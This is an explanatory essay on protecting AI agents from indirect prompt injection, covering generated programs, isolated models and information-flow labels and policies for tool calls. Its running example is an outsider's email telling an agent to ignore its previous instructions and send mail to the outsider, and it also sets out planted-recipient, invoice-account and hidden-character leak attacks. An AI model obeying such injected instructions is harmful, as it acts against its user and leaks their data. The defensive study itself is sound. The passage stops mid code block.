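# Letting a language model move data between tools by writing code that can be checked

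## How data normally reaches a tool, and what changes when the model writes code

A language model takes in text and produces more text, one token (a word or a piece of a word) at a time. Its context is all the text it receives for its next output. A model can only write text on its own, so developers connect it to tools, which are programs or services that run when the model writes a request for them, such as a function that reads a mailbox or one that sends an email. An agent is an assistant that works through a task by having a model choose which tools to call.

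Most agents move data between tools by passing it through the model. For example, the text of an email enters the model's context, and the model writes out whatever part the next tool needs. The model can instead write a short program that fetches the emails and passes them to the next tool. Ordinary software can run this program without showing the model what the emails contain, so a stranger's email has much less influence over what the agent does. Somebody can also inspect the program before it runs, which isn't possible with decisions the model hasn't made yet.

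### The tool-calling loop

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) describe the usual procedure in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. The application sends the model a description of each tool and its parameters, along with a list of messages that includes a system message with the developer's instructions and a user message with the task. The model replies either in plain language or with structured text that names a tool and supplies its arguments. The application treats this structured text as a request and decides whether to make the call. If it makes the call, it adds the result to the list as a new message and sends the whole list back to the model. This repeats until the model produces a final answer for the user.

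In their notation a model M is a function:

```
M : Msg* × F*  →  ToolCall F str*  |  Assistant str
```

Here Msg* is the list of messages so far, F* is the list of tools, and str* is a list of character strings. The function returns either a tool call with string arguments or a reply to the user. Because the function takes the full list of messages, any message can affect any later call. The model writes the arguments itself, and in the basic form of the loop they go to the tool unchanged, so the model can pass on an email only by writing it out again.

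Costa and colleagues illustrate the danger with an ordinary piece of office work. A user asks the agent to summarise recent emails on the progress of Project X and send the summary to the user's manager. The loop runs as follows:

1. The model receives the request and asks for a call to the tool that reads emails.
2. The application makes the call and adds the text of the emails to the context.
3. The model reads the emails, composes a summary, and asks for a call to the tool that sends email, with the manager's address and the summary as arguments.
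4. The application sends the message, and the model tells the user that the job is done.

Now suppose an outsider wrote one of the emails and included an instruction for the agent to ignore its previous instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to the outsider's address. At step 3, that instruction is in the same context as the user's request, and the model may act on it.

### What the loop costs

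The outsider's sentence is a prompt injection, text that someone places in a model's input to make it act against the wishes of the user or developer. *Foundational Challenges in Assuring Alignment and Safety of Large Language Models* (2024), a review of open problems, sorts these attacks by who carries them out. In direct prompt injection, the user tries to get around limits that the application's developer has set. In indirect prompt injection, a third party controls a source of data that the model reads, such as a web page or, in the Project X case, an email. The indirect kind is the main concern for an email assistant. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) points out that the assistant acts with the user's own access, so the user gains nothing by attacking it.

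The outsider's attack defeats both integrity and confidentiality. Integrity here means protecting actions from untrusted influence, and it fails when the outsider's sentence determines which call the model asks for. Confidentiality means protecting data from unauthorised readers, and it fails a moment later, when the top email is sent to the outsider's address. Some attackers only need to defeat integrity. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give two examples that don't reveal any secrets: sending an email in the user's name that asks a coworker to approve a security-sensitive action, and deleting a message that the user needed to see.

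Language models have no mechanism to enforce the obvious remedy, which is to treat emails as data and take instructions only from the user. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) notes that a conventional computer can keep code in memory that programs may execute but not overwrite, so that data from an attacker does not run as code. A language model receives everything as text, and any token of the input can in principle influence every token of the output. *Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?* (2024) traces the lack of separation partly to developers having built these models as chatbots that follow instructions wherever they occur in the input.

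Developers can train a model to respect the difference between instructions and data, or mark untrusted text with delimiters and warnings. These measures help, but *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* objects that if the separation holds only with some probability, an attacker can run an optimiser to search for inputs on which it fails. The paper adds that even a perfect separation would stop a large share of prompt injections without fully solving the problem. Part of the difficulty is defining the separation, since a user who asks an agent to complete today's entries in a to-do app wants it to act on text it finds in the data. Newer models have not removed the problem. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (May 2026) still lists the separation as an open research problem and adds "if attainable". *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*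 (June 2026) describes delimiters and role labels as useful engineering practice that creates no hard security boundary.

The loop exposes data even when nobody attacks it. Whatever the email tool returns goes into the model's context and, if the model is an online service, to the provider's servers. Costa and colleagues leave this exposure out of their threat model, since they treat the model as trusted and assume that adversaries do not directly observe what passes to and from it. That is reasonable for studying prompt injection, but an office that may not show its clients' correspondence to an outside provider still has to prevent this exposure.

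Copying data between tools through the model also uses tokens. The model reads the emails in full, reads them again on every later turn, and uses more tokens to write data into the next call. Each time it rewrites the data, it may also drop a digit from an account number or shorten a quotation. When one tool's result can go straight to another, keeping the data out of the context avoids this token use. However, total token use doesn't always fall. Costa and colleagues report that in their own system, which hides some data from the main model, calls to a second model add turns and so increase delay and token use.

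### The same task as a three-line program

Instead of requesting one call at a time, the model could answer the Project X request with this:

```
emails  = read_emails(topic="Project X")
summary = isolated_model("Summarise the progress reported here", emails)
send_email(to=manager, body=summary)
```

The planning model is the language model that turns the user's request into this program. The application keeps it from reading protected data, so it handles only the names `emails` and `summary`. The runtime, which is conventional software, executes the program and holds the real values. The address in `manager` comes from the user's own settings. On the second line, the runtime passes the emails to an isolated model, a second language model that has no tools.

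Costa and colleagues use the same three steps for a very similar task, but their system keeps the loop. The planning model requests the calls one by one and receives the name of each result instead of the result itself. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues write the steps as one program, in their case for an assistant that sends the day's calendar to the user's boss. Both arrangements keep the strangers' text away from the model that chooses the calls. Writing the steps as one program also means that the whole plan exists before the first call, when it can still be rejected.

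| | Ordinary loop | Generated program |
|---|---|---|
| What the model has read when it chooses the sending step | The request, the tool descriptions and every email | The request and the tool descriptions |
| Route of the emails' text | Into the model's context, then out again in the model's own words | From the email tool to the runtime, and from there to the isolated model |
| How the recipient comes about | The model writes an address after reading the emails | The program names the manager before anyone reads an email |
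| What the outsider's email can change | The tool, the recipient and the text | The text of the summary |

The last row shows a limit. The isolated model reads the outsider's email and may follow instructions in it. It cannot send anything, but it can write a bad summary, which the runtime will deliver to the manager. The outsider therefore can no longer choose the recipient but still has some influence over what the manager reads. Costa and colleagues mention an email that tells the isolated model to produce an empty summary, and Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge that the content of the message in their calendar program is open to the same manipulation.

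The gain in privacy also depends on details the three lines do not show. If one company hosts both models, it still receives the emails. If the user had asked the agent to forward the emails unchanged, the code would not need the second line, and no model would need to read them.

The case for generated programs also depends on a reviewer being able to establish what a program can do with data without trusting its author. This is easy to believe of the Project X program, which reads emails once and sends one message to the manager. Only the body of that message is derived from the emails. These facts follow from the program's text and from what the runtime does with each line, so they hold even if the planning model was careless or manipulated. A checker, which is conventional software that accepts or rejects a program before it runs, could reach the same conclusion.

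*Foundational Challenges in Assuring Alignment and Safety of Large Language Models* gives a general reason to expect this to work for code and not for a plan in English, in a discussion of how to make a model's reasoning open to inspection. Each construct in a programming language has a mathematically exact meaning, so formal verification tools can work on it, while the meaning of an English sentence shifts with its context. The same discussion includes two reservations that apply here. First, someone still has to translate the user's request into the program, and that step is as ambiguous as the request was. A check can show that a program sends one summary to the manager, but not that the user meant it to. Second, some computations may be too complex for any program that a person could read, which leaves opaque components inside the program. The isolated model on the second line is one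 such component. A reviewer can establish where its output goes but not whether the output is true.

### From plugins to "code-then-execute"

In 2023, ChatGPT users could access tools through what OpenAI called plugins. *LLM Platform Security* (Iqbal et al., 2023) describes how data reached them. The platform loaded each plugin's description into the context, and the model picked the plugin whose description best matched the user's command and sent it the data. The platform and plugin communicated from server to server, so the user saw only the end result. The descriptions were in natural language, which a model can interpret too broadly or too narrowly. Iqbal and colleagues also judged OpenAI's review of third-party plugins to be weak, partly on anecdotal evidence.

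In April of that year, the programmer Simon Willison published a blog post, *The Dual LLM Pattern for Building AI Assistants that Can Resist Prompt Injection*, about the danger of combining tools with untrusted web pages. The best defence at the time was to ask the user to approve each action. He doubted that this would work, because assistants are meant to remove tedium and people would soon click "OK" on everything. He instead proposed dividing the work between two models, in the way the Project X program does.

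Systems in which the model writes code to call tools appeared at about the same time, though not as a defence. *TaskWeaver* (2023) presents a framework in which the model receives a description of each plugin and writes Python code that calls it, without needing to know how the plugin works inside. The paper reports that the model may generate code that disregards explicit instructions in the prompt, such as an instruction not to modify local files. Having a model write code therefore provides no security by itself, and something outside the model has to examine or confine the code.

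In the 2024 review, these ideas were still separate. Its section on the missing boundary between instructions and data treats the problem as an open question and considers four remedies: tags that mark parts of the input, Willison's two models, training, and filtering. None of them has the model write a program, although the review makes the argument about the exact meaning of code a few pages earlier.

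The two lines of work came together in March 2025, when *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, by Debenedetti and colleagues, described a system named CaMeL. According to Costa and colleagues, CaMeL combines a planner that works in code with ideas similar to Willison's. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, three of whom also wrote the CaMeL paper, then named the general approach "code-then-execute" and cited CaMeL as an example.

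Code-then-execute is one of six design patterns that share a principle. Once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger an action with harmful side effects. In the simplest pattern, "action-selector", the model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results. In "plan-then-execute", the model commits to a list of calls before it reads untrusted data, so the data can change the contents of a call but not which calls are made. "LLM map-reduce" gives each document to its own isolated model and accepts only a narrow answer, such as whether the file is an invoice. It is a special case of Willison's "dual LLM" pattern. Code-then-execute is the fullest form of the dual LLM pattern, and it generalises plan-then-execute by replacing the list of calls with a full program. "Context-minimization" removes the user's prompt from the context before the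 model writes its answer, which guards against some direct injections.

A program can express plans that a fixed list cannot, as an example from Beurer-Kellner and colleagues shows. A user asks the assistant to tell all regular collaborators about a vacation next week. Nobody knows at the outset how many messages that will take or who will receive them, so the plan has to work out the recipients from past emails and meetings, then repeat the sending step for each. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider it very unlikely that an email assistant should ever let untrusted data decide which actions it takes and in what order, and they expect that preventing this would make the assistant only slightly less useful. However, their overview assigns code-then-execute to only two of their ten case studies, the email and calendar assistant and a booking assistant.

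The pattern does not protect against hostile text in the request itself. A user may paste a paragraph from an attacker's website into the instruction without noticing the injection it contains. The planning model then reads the injection directly and may write the program the attacker wants. Keeping protected data away from the planning model does not prevent this, so the defence has to come from checking the program before it runs or blocking its calls while it runs.

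## Labelling the data and stating the rules

The last line of the Project X program sends a summary of some emails to the manager. This is a leak if the manager isn't allowed to read those emails, and the program's text doesn't show whether they are. Before a checker or a runtime can check the program, a person has to write down who is allowed to read each piece of data, who could have influenced it, and what each tool is allowed to receive. Labels are the marks on the data, and a policy is a rule about which labelled data may go into which call.

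Costa and colleagues work out such a scheme for FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System), which they built at Microsoft. FIDES decides whether to allow each tool call by comparing labels, without using a language model, so the same labels always produce the same decision. It keeps the tool-calling loop, but its labels and policies also apply to generated programs, because those programs act through tool calls with arguments too.

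### Labels, their order and their join

The scheme is much older than language models. In *Secure Computer Systems*, Bell and LaPadula (1973) modelled a computer mathematically and defined security and compromise precisely. Later work takes from them the rule that secret data must not flow anywhere that isn't cleared for it. K. J. Biba applied the same idea to integrity in MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), where the rule is that untrustworthy data must not flow into anything that has to be trustworthy.

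Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976) gives a general model with a set of security classes, a relation that holds when information in one class may flow into another, and an operator that gives the class of a result computed from two inputs. In FIDES, the classes are labels. A ⊑ B means that data labelled A may flow to a place labelled B, and the join, A ⊔ B, is the label of a result computed from data labelled A and data labelled B.

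Denning shows that these parts have to fit together. If a program may copy `a` into `b` and `b` into `c`, then copying `a` straight into `c` must be legal too, or else a program could get round the ban by copying in two steps. The label of a result must also be at least as strict as the label of each input, and no stricter than that requires. Under these conditions the labels form a lattice, an ordered set in which any two labels have a least upper bound. (A full lattice also has greatest lower bounds, which FIDES does not need.)

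This makes a reviewer's work easier in two ways. A sequence of steps is secure if each step is secure, so a checker can go through a program line by line. Data from several sources may flow to a destination exactly when the data from each source may flow there on its own, so the checker can compare the joined label once instead of checking every email's label separately.

The smallest useful lattices have two labels each: public and secret for confidentiality, trusted (T) and untrusted (U) for integrity. An office needs finer distinctions, and for these Costa and colleagues use sets of people:

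```
confidentiality:  label = the people who may read the data
                  join  = intersection
integrity:        label = the people who may have written the data
                  join  = union
```

A person may read a mixture only if they may read every ingredient, which is why the reader sets intersect. Anyone who could have written one ingredient may have influenced the mixture, which is why the writer sets unite. For Project X, with one email from Ana and one from Ben, the result is:

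```
Ana's email   readers {user, manager, Ana}   writers {Ana}
Ben's email   readers {user, manager, Ben}   writers {Ben}
summary       readers {user, manager}        writers {Ana, Ben}
```

The check allows the summary to be sent to the manager, who is in the reader set. It blocks sending the summary to an outsider or to Ana. Ana wrote half of the material, but the summary may repeat what Ben told only the user and the manager.

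The summary gets the full join even if the isolated model used only Ana's email, since nobody can reliably tell which part of the input shaped the output. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026), a system that checks a complete plan before any tool runs, follows the same rule. Girrens and Wang point out that this prevents the isolated model from "laundering" an attacker's text into something that looks trustworthy. Their integrity order puts trusted data at the top instead of the bottom, but combined data still gets the label of its least trusted input.

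Suppose the summary also draws on the outsider's email from the earlier attack. If that email's readers are its sender and its recipient, its label is {outsider, user}, and the summary's reader set shrinks to {user}. The outsider cannot widen the audience for anyone else's data, because intersecting reader sets never adds a reader. But on a strict reading of the labels, one stray email about Project X is enough to stop the manager from being allowed to read the summary. Whether the sending step then fails depends on the policy.

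### Two policies and what each one misses

Each piece of data in FIDES has an integrity label and a confidentiality label. Each tool call also has an integrity label, which depends on what the model had read when it chose the call. The sending call is therefore untrusted in the ordinary loop, where the model has read the emails, and trusted in the generated program.

Costa and colleagues define two basic policies over these labels. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, give them short names, "trusted action" and "permitted flow":

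```
trusted action:   the call and all its arguments have integrity T
permitted flow:   recipients ⊆ readers of the data sent
```

The first policy applies to consequential calls, such as deleting a message or paying a bill. The second applies to calls that send data to recipients, such as the addressees of an email or the members of a group chat.

Permitted flow alone does not stop prompt injection. It only limits what a hijacked agent can reveal, so it allows both of the earlier attacks that reveal no secrets: the deleted message and the email asking a coworker for approval.

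Trusted action alone, by contrast, does not stop a program from leaking confidential data. Costa and colleagues give the example of a company database whose records are both trusted and confidential. A program that posts such a record on a public page satisfies the policy, because nobody untrusted influenced the call or its contents.

Costa and colleagues treat this second gap as partly desirable, because users sometimes want to send confidential material to somebody new, such as an outside lawyer. Deliberately releasing protected data to readers who could not otherwise have it is called declassification. If it can happen only in a trusted context, an attacker who controls untrusted data cannot cause it. Costa and colleagues say such releases can be assumed to be intentional, and they describe this as a form of robust declassification, citing a 2004 paper by Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic.

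That assumption overstates how reliable the planning model is. Costa and colleagues note that models misread requests even when all the data is trusted, and a misread request can send a client's file to the wrong person even when there is no attacker. An office with a legal duty of confidentiality should therefore require both policies for tools that send data out, and accept that the system will refuse some releases the user wanted.

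FIDES offers both combinations. The permissive one allows a call that satisfies either policy, while the restrictive one requires the call to satisfy both. For their tests, Costa and colleagues assigned a policy to each of 27 tools. Five tools that send or write content, including `send_email`, got the permissive combination. One tool, which adds participants to a calendar event, got the restrictive combination. The other 21, including `delete_email` and `send_money`, got a version of trusted action.

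Under the permissive combination, the outsider's stray email no longer blocks the summary. The reader set has shrunk to the user, but the call goes ahead because it comes from a trusted context. The drawback is that an agent in an untrusted context may still send messages to permitted readers. Costa and colleagues accept this for chat messages but add a ban on sending untrusted links, since a link can carry data to whoever runs the website.

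### Separate limits for recipient and body

Taken literally, the trusted action rule also blocks the legitimate summary, because it requires every argument to be trusted and the body of the message comes from email that strangers can write. It also blocks any other task that passes on outside material, such as forwarding a newsletter or reporting the result of a web search.

The remedy is to set a limit for each argument. Costa and colleagues suggest that a message tool could require a trusted call and a trusted recipient while accepting a body that depends on untrusted content. Kolluri and colleagues give this a general form, in which a policy lists one maximum label for the call and one for each argument, and the call passes if every actual label is at or below its maximum. For the Project X program, a reviewer could write:

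```
send_email(to, body)
    the call   integrity T
    to         integrity T
    body       any integrity; readers must include everyone in "to"
```

The summary now passes. The call and the address are both trusted. The body is untrusted, but this policy allows that, and the manager is among the body's readers when it uses the two emails from Ana and Ben.

Separate limits for each argument are useful only if the arguments can have different labels. In the ordinary loop, the model writes all the arguments after reading the same context, so a basic label-tracking agent has to give them all that context's label. When the program passes data by name, the recipient keeps the label of the user's settings and the body keeps the label of the emails.

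The policies in the FIDES tests were looser than this. Their version of trusted action looks only at the label of the call and ignores the labels of the arguments. Consider a program that finds its recipient in the mail:

```
address = isolated_model("Find the client's address", emails)
send_email(to=address, body=report)
```

The planning model wrote both lines in a trusted context, so the call is trusted and the permissive combination allows it. But an outsider who plants an address in an email may receive the report. The release is no longer robust, because untrusted data determined the recipient. A reviewer who wants to allow deliberate releases can prevent this by waiving the check on readers only when both the call and the recipient are trusted.

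`send_money` has the same weakness under the tested policy. Girrens and Wang use such a case as their motivating example. An invoice contains the attacker's bank account, and the agent pays into that account while following exactly the steps the user wanted, so the attack needs no hidden instruction in the invoice.

The next table compares the policies on four calls. The last column applies the permissive combination to `send_email` and the tested version of trusted action to `delete_email`.

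| Call | Trusted action, all arguments | Permitted flow alone | Separate limits | FIDES as tested |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A program emails the summary to the manager | Blocked | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| An agent that has read the outsider's email deletes a message | Blocked | Passes | Blocked | Blocked |
| A program emails a trusted, confidential record to an outsider | Passes | Blocked | Blocked | Passes |
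| A program emails the summary to an address the outsider planted | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked | Passes |

### Where the labels come from

All these verdicts depend on labels, and most office data arrives without any. Costa and colleagues infer the readers of an email from its sender and recipient addresses. They acknowledge that somebody may have shared the email more widely, which would make the label stricter than necessary. For integrity, they mention that mail servers can authenticate a sender's address under a DMARC policy (a standard against forged senders) and that outsiders cannot tamper with some system-generated timestamps.

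Costa and colleagues wrapped each tool in a function that labels data as the tool reads it. A label can cover the whole result or a single field, so one record can contain a trusted date and an untrusted subject line. Kolluri and colleagues labelled web pages in a similar way, marking whatever users had posted as untrusted and the site's own buttons and text boxes as trusted.

An email's exact readers are known only once the tool fetches it, so a check before the code runs needs a label for whatever the tool might return. Girrens and Wang therefore give each tool a baseline output label. The tool's inputs are not enough to determine this label, because a search with a harmless query may return confidential files, and a web search returns untrusted text whatever the query.

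The user's request also needs a label, and FIDES treats it as trusted and public by default. Trusting the request makes sense for a system that acts on the user's behalf, but any injection the user pastes into it is then labelled trusted too. Because the request is labelled public, the program is allowed to send anyone a salary that the user types into it. Costa and colleagues say that developers can choose other labels where appropriate, and an office that handles personal data probably should.

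Costa and colleagues ran their experiments on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks with attacks hidden in the data. They labelled a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. This gives a clear baseline for comparing agents, but it relies on knowing in advance where the attacks will be, which no office can do. The results therefore show what the policies do when the labels are right, but give little evidence of how often a deployer would label the data correctly.

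If a label is too strict, the system blocks safe work. In one AgentDojo task, the user wants a password-reset link from the mailbox, and FIDES failed to return the correct one because it could not distinguish trusted senders from untrusted ones. The system can also approve an unsafe call, with no sign of a problem, if the label is too lax. Suppose a company marks its shared project folder as trusted and later gives a contractor permission to edit it. Every program that takes a recipient or an account number from that folder still passes, because the checker uses only the label, not the text.

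Designers may want to let a system upgrade labels. Costa and colleagues mention running a document through a prompt-injection detector and marking it as trusted if the detector finds nothing, but they warn that relying on detectors can weaken the security guarantees. An attacker who can fool the detector gets a trusted label for hostile text. The user can also vouch for a document, which Kolluri and colleagues call endorsement. They decided against an equivalent for confidentiality, because whether it is right to release private data usually depends on the particular recipient and occasion.

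A correct integrity label records who could have influenced the data, but data labelled "trusted" can still be wrong. Purdue University's *Integrity*, a set of lecture slides on Biba's report, notes that a program can introduce bad data without having read any, whereas it cannot leak a secret it has not read. For example, an isolated model that summarises only trusted documents can still invent a figure, and the summary will be labelled trusted.

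### One flow rule or a rule for each tool

The person who deploys the system normally writes the policies. Girrens and Wang don't let the tools' suppliers write them, because a malicious tool could then come with a policy that allows it to receive any data. The deployer must choose between one general rule for all tools and separate rules for each.

SPA's single flow rule lets data flow to a destination if the destination is cleared for data of that confidentiality and the data is at least as trustworthy as the destination requires. The deployer defines the labels and gives each tool a maximum confidentiality level, a minimum integrity level and a baseline output label. The rule never changes, so a reviewer can study it once and then go through a table of tool settings.

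The other approach is to write separate policy logic for each tool. Girrens and Wang put CaMeL in this category. By their account, it records where each value came from and who may receive it, and each tool's policy can test those records in whatever way it needs. Such policies can express conditions that a comparison of labels cannot. But the security guarantee then depends on every policy being correct and complete, and a mistake in one may not show up in the others.

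SPA sets one integrity minimum for a whole tool and rejects a call if any argument falls below it. In the Project X example, if `send_email` requires trusted input, SPA rejects the summary email because its body is untrusted. If `send_email` accepts untrusted input, SPA also accepts a recipient that came from an outsider's email. No setting allows the untrusted body but rejects the untrusted recipient. Girrens and Wang list requirements for individual arguments among the improvements still to be made.

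In their measurements on AgentDojo, switching on the label checks reduced the share of tasks completed when there was no attack from 53.0% to 29.0%. About 53% of all runs stopped at the check, typically because a plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that required more trusted data. FIDES avoided many such refusals by not checking arguments, which is also why it accepted the planted address. The two systems used different models and designs, so their scores do not reflect the policies alone.

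Limits for each argument, in the form Kolluri and colleagues use, are probably the best starting point. The comparison stays the same for every tool, and the reviewer can still treat an address differently from a paragraph of text. This approach requires more entries, because someone has to decide for every argument of every tool whether an outsider may influence it, and for every outgoing argument who will see it. A few templates cover most cases, as the 27 tools in the FIDES tests show, but the right choice can also depend on the application and on what the user asked for.

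Whichever form the deployer chooses, the labels and policies are among the trusted components. Girrens and Wang state that incorrect policies can reject safe work or admit unsafe work. They say work remains to be done on inferring policies automatically, auditing configurations and testing how well a system copes with wrong labels.

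## Deciding what the model may see

The designer has to decide what to show the planning model before it writes anything, and labels help with this decision too. The model should see only what the task requires, because anything in its context can influence its calls or appear in what it writes. For many tasks, the request and the tool descriptions are enough.

### Tasks a model can plan without seeing the data

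Costa and colleagues give a test for such tasks. They treat a task t as a request, a list of tools and a set D of possible starting states, such as all the mailboxes the user might have. For each state d, ⟦t⟧ d is the set of action sequences that would complete the task. The task is data independent if at least one sequence works in every state:

```
⋂ ⟦t⟧ d  ≠  ∅        over every d in D
```

The sequences contain the tool calls and the final reply, but not queries to the model, which don't affect whether the task gets done. If no single sequence works in every state, the task is data dependent, and the planner has to learn something about the data before it can choose its calls.

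Forwarding the top three emails passes the test because the agent reads three emails and sends them on, whatever they contain. Summarising the emails and sending the summary also passes, with the agent calling the isolated model between reading and sending. Carrying out the tasks due today in a to-do list fails because the right tools depend on what is in the list. One entry may require a payment and another a hotel booking.

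The forwarded text differs from one mailbox to another, so the test gives the intended result only if a call can refer to data without containing it. "Send the result of the first call" then counts as the same call in every state.

Tasks pass more often in some kinds of work than in others. Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's 97 user tasks by hand and found that 5% of the office tasks and 10% of the travel tasks were data dependent. The share was about 43% for both banking and chat, where users often ask the agent to read a file or web page and follow the instructions in it. The pattern therefore suits an email and calendar assistant much better than one that pays bills according to instructions in a document.

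In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) narrow the definition of a data-dependent task for agents that operate a web browser. A task counts as data dependent only if the choice of calls or arguments depends on untrusted or non-public data. An agent that reads a shop's opening hours on a trusted public page and then picks a time still has a data-independent task. This test is more useful to a designer because showing the model trusted, public data doesn't weaken protection.

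### Passing results by name

For a data-independent task, the planning model can work with names alone. Costa and colleagues describe a "variable passing" planner that does this inside the tool-calling loop. For the request to forward three emails, it works as follows:

1. The planning model asks for `read_emails(number=3)`.
2. The runtime makes the call, creates a fresh name such as `#read_emails_0`, and stores the emails under that name in its own memory.
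3. The runtime adds a message to the model's context that contains only the name.
4. The model asks for `send_message(to=user, message=#read_emails_0)`.
5. The runtime replaces the name with the emails and their label, checks the policy, and calls the tool.

The model can see from the name which tool produced the value and, where relevant, which field it is, as in `#read_emails_0.subject`. The model can still misspell a name or invent one. Constrained decoding, in which software restricts the model at each token to continuations that fit a required format, can prevent this if the format allows only names that exist. Costa and colleagues did not use it in their tests, where the model sometimes confused one name with another.

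Showing the model a name in place of a result hides the content but can still reveal its shape, such as the number of items. In one published FIDES trace, a user asks the agent to find the chat channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. The runtime hides the channel names and every message, but the model can see how many hidden items each result contains. One channel returns an empty list, and the model adds Alice to it. Anyone who can post in a channel can change its message count, so outsiders have some influence over which channel she joins.

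A generated program avoids this particular exposure. The planning model chooses variable names as it writes the program, before any tool has run, so it receives nothing back at steps 2 and 3. If the task requires counting messages, the program can count them without the model ever seeing the totals.

### Hiding only what would raise the label

Hiding every result is safe but wasteful, since much of what tools return is harmless. FIDES therefore compares each result's label with the label of the current context. If showing the result would make the context's label stricter, the runtime stores the result under a name. Otherwise, it applies the same test to each part of the result. The model might then see an email's trusted timestamp next to a name that stands for its untrusted subject line. The context's label stays the same.

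Zverev and colleagues write the rule out for a value with integrity I and readers R:

```
hide the value if
    the context is trusted and I is untrusted,   or
    some permitted reader of the context is not in R
```

Their example is a web shop's product page with a price, a customer review and the last digits of the user's saved card. The agent starts with a trusted, public context. It sees the price, but the runtime hides the review, because a stranger wrote it, and the card digits, because only the user and the shop may read them. If the agent asks to see the digits, the runtime shows them and limits the context's readers to the user and the shop. The review stays hidden because the context is still trusted.

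In the FIDES tests, Costa and colleagues applied only the integrity half of this rule. They hid untrusted data from the planning model but left confidentiality to the policies on outgoing calls, so a trusted but confidential company record would have entered the model's context in full. An office that wants to keep such records from the model needs to apply the confidentiality half too.

When the model writes a whole program in advance, the designer can apply the same rule to whatever goes into the context beforehand. If the context is public, it can include today's date but not the names of the user's private mail folders. The designer could instead start with a context that only the user may read, but any text the model writes into a message would then have the same restricted label.

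A model that sees only part of the data may also guess. In one banking task, the user asks what a New Year's gift cost, and the runtime hides the descriptions of all the transactions. The model saw a single payment dated 1 January and reported its amount, which was correct. On different data the same guess could be wrong, and the reply would look just as confident. Costa and colleagues told the version of their planner that cannot inspect data to stop and say so when a task requires inspecting it. A designer should give the planning model a way to do the same, whether it replies in a loop or writes a program.

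### From the Dual LLM proposal to a line of code

Summarizing data requires a model that reads it, so the isolated model does this. Willison's 2023 proposal calls the planning model "privileged", the isolated model "quarantined" and the runtime the "controller". His controller already passed results by name. It stored an email as `$VAR1`, gave the email to the quarantined model, stored the summary as `$VAR2`, and inserted the summary's text only when displaying it to the user.

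Willison assumed that the quarantined model could "go rogue at any moment", so its unfiltered output must never reach the privileged model. This holds even if other models have processed the output first, because an injection can survive each step. He called his own design "pretty bad" and worried most about its complexity, since a single programming mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model wastes the whole effort. In a note added in April 2025, he wrote that the CaMeL paper had identified a potential flaw in his proposal and described a more evolved system.

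Later systems let the planner call the second model like any other tool. In FIDES, the planner sends it a question and a list of names, and the answer comes back under a new name. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues put the call into a program, as on the second line of the Project X example. Girrens and Wang make the call one step of a plan. Their planner writes the question and names the inputs, while the isolated model keeps fixed general instructions and has no memory of the rest of the plan.

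The isolated model can summarise, translate, extract a date or sort messages into groups. It cannot send, delete or look anything up, and it can pass information to the planner only through the channel the designer provides. A hostile email can still control its answers, as with the Project X summary, and those answers can include any other data the model was given. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that a manipulated isolated model could hide sensitive data in a draft reply, for instance by using invisible characters. A program should therefore give each call only the data it needs. Using a separate call for each document also prevents one hostile file from changing the answers about the others.

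#### Running it locally or at a provider

The protection against prompt injection is the same wherever the isolated model runs, because it depends on the model having no tools and on what the runtime does with its answer. A hosted model counts as isolated only if the developer turns off any built-in tools, such as web search.

Privacy depends a great deal on where the isolated model runs. If it runs on the office's own machines, the emails stay there. The planning model can still be a large hosted one, because it receives only the request, the tool descriptions and perhaps some names. If a provider hosts the isolated model, the provider receives every email the program passes to that model. Zverev and colleagues, like Costa and colleagues, trust the provider, so neither SPIDES nor FIDES prevents this. An office can make the exposure visible by treating the provider as a recipient. The call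 to the isolated model then needs a policy, like the one for `send_email`, that checks that the provider may read the input.

A local model may be less capable than a hosted one. Both teams used the same model in both roles, so their results don't show how much quality an office would lose by choosing a smaller one for the isolated role. But hosted models are subject to the provider's safety filters. Zverev and colleagues found that these sometimes blocked Claude Opus 5 and Opus 5.5 from handling attachments with login details or phishing messages. Hiding the attachments from the main model avoided some of these refusals, but when the isolated model had to analyse a phishing message, the filters could still block it, causing the task to fail.

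### Answers in a fixed form

Some tasks need only a small fact from the data. Suppose a user asks the agent to check the latest three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, to block the time in the calendar. This task is data dependent because the right sequence of calls depends on whether there is a request. In FIDES, the planner sends the isolated model a yes-or-no question, then reads the answer without ever reading the emails.

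In 2023, Willison allowed the controller to pass on the quarantined model's output if the model sorts text into a fixed set of categories, because the controller can first confirm that the output is one of them. FIDES lets the planner specify the form of the answer and uses constrained decoding to enforce it.

The form limits how much an answer can carry. An answer with n possible values carries at most log₂ n bits of information:

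| Form of the answer | Most it can carry |
|---|---|
| Yes or no (a Boolean) | 1 bit |
| One of three listed actions | About 1.58 bits |
| A whole number from 0 to 10 | About 3.46 bits |
| Any 64-bit integer | 64 bits, enough for eight characters of plain text |
| Free text | No fixed bound |

Costa and colleagues give an example of the second row, in which the isolated model chooses whether to schedule a meeting, send an out-of-office reply or forward the email. In practice, the menu also needs a "none of these" entry, because otherwise the model has to pick an action even when the email asks for nothing. This fourth entry raises the limit to 2 bits.

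FIDES makes the form part of the label. Each value has a type in addition to its integrity and confidentiality, and the types are ordered by how much they can carry: a Boolean is below a three-way choice, which is below free text. A policy can then treat untrusted answers differently according to their type. For the calendar request, it could look like this:

```
create_event(time)
    the call   integrity T, or integrity U with type Boolean
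    time       any integrity
```

The policy allows the call if the untrusted emails influenced it only through a yes-or-no answer. If the planner had asked "What should I do about these emails?" and acted on the free-text reply, the policy would refuse the call because it would have integrity U with type text. The event's time may come from a stranger, which is acceptable here because the event has no other participants and appears only in the user's calendar.

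A generated program can do this without showing the planning model even the one bit:

```
emails = read_emails(number=3)
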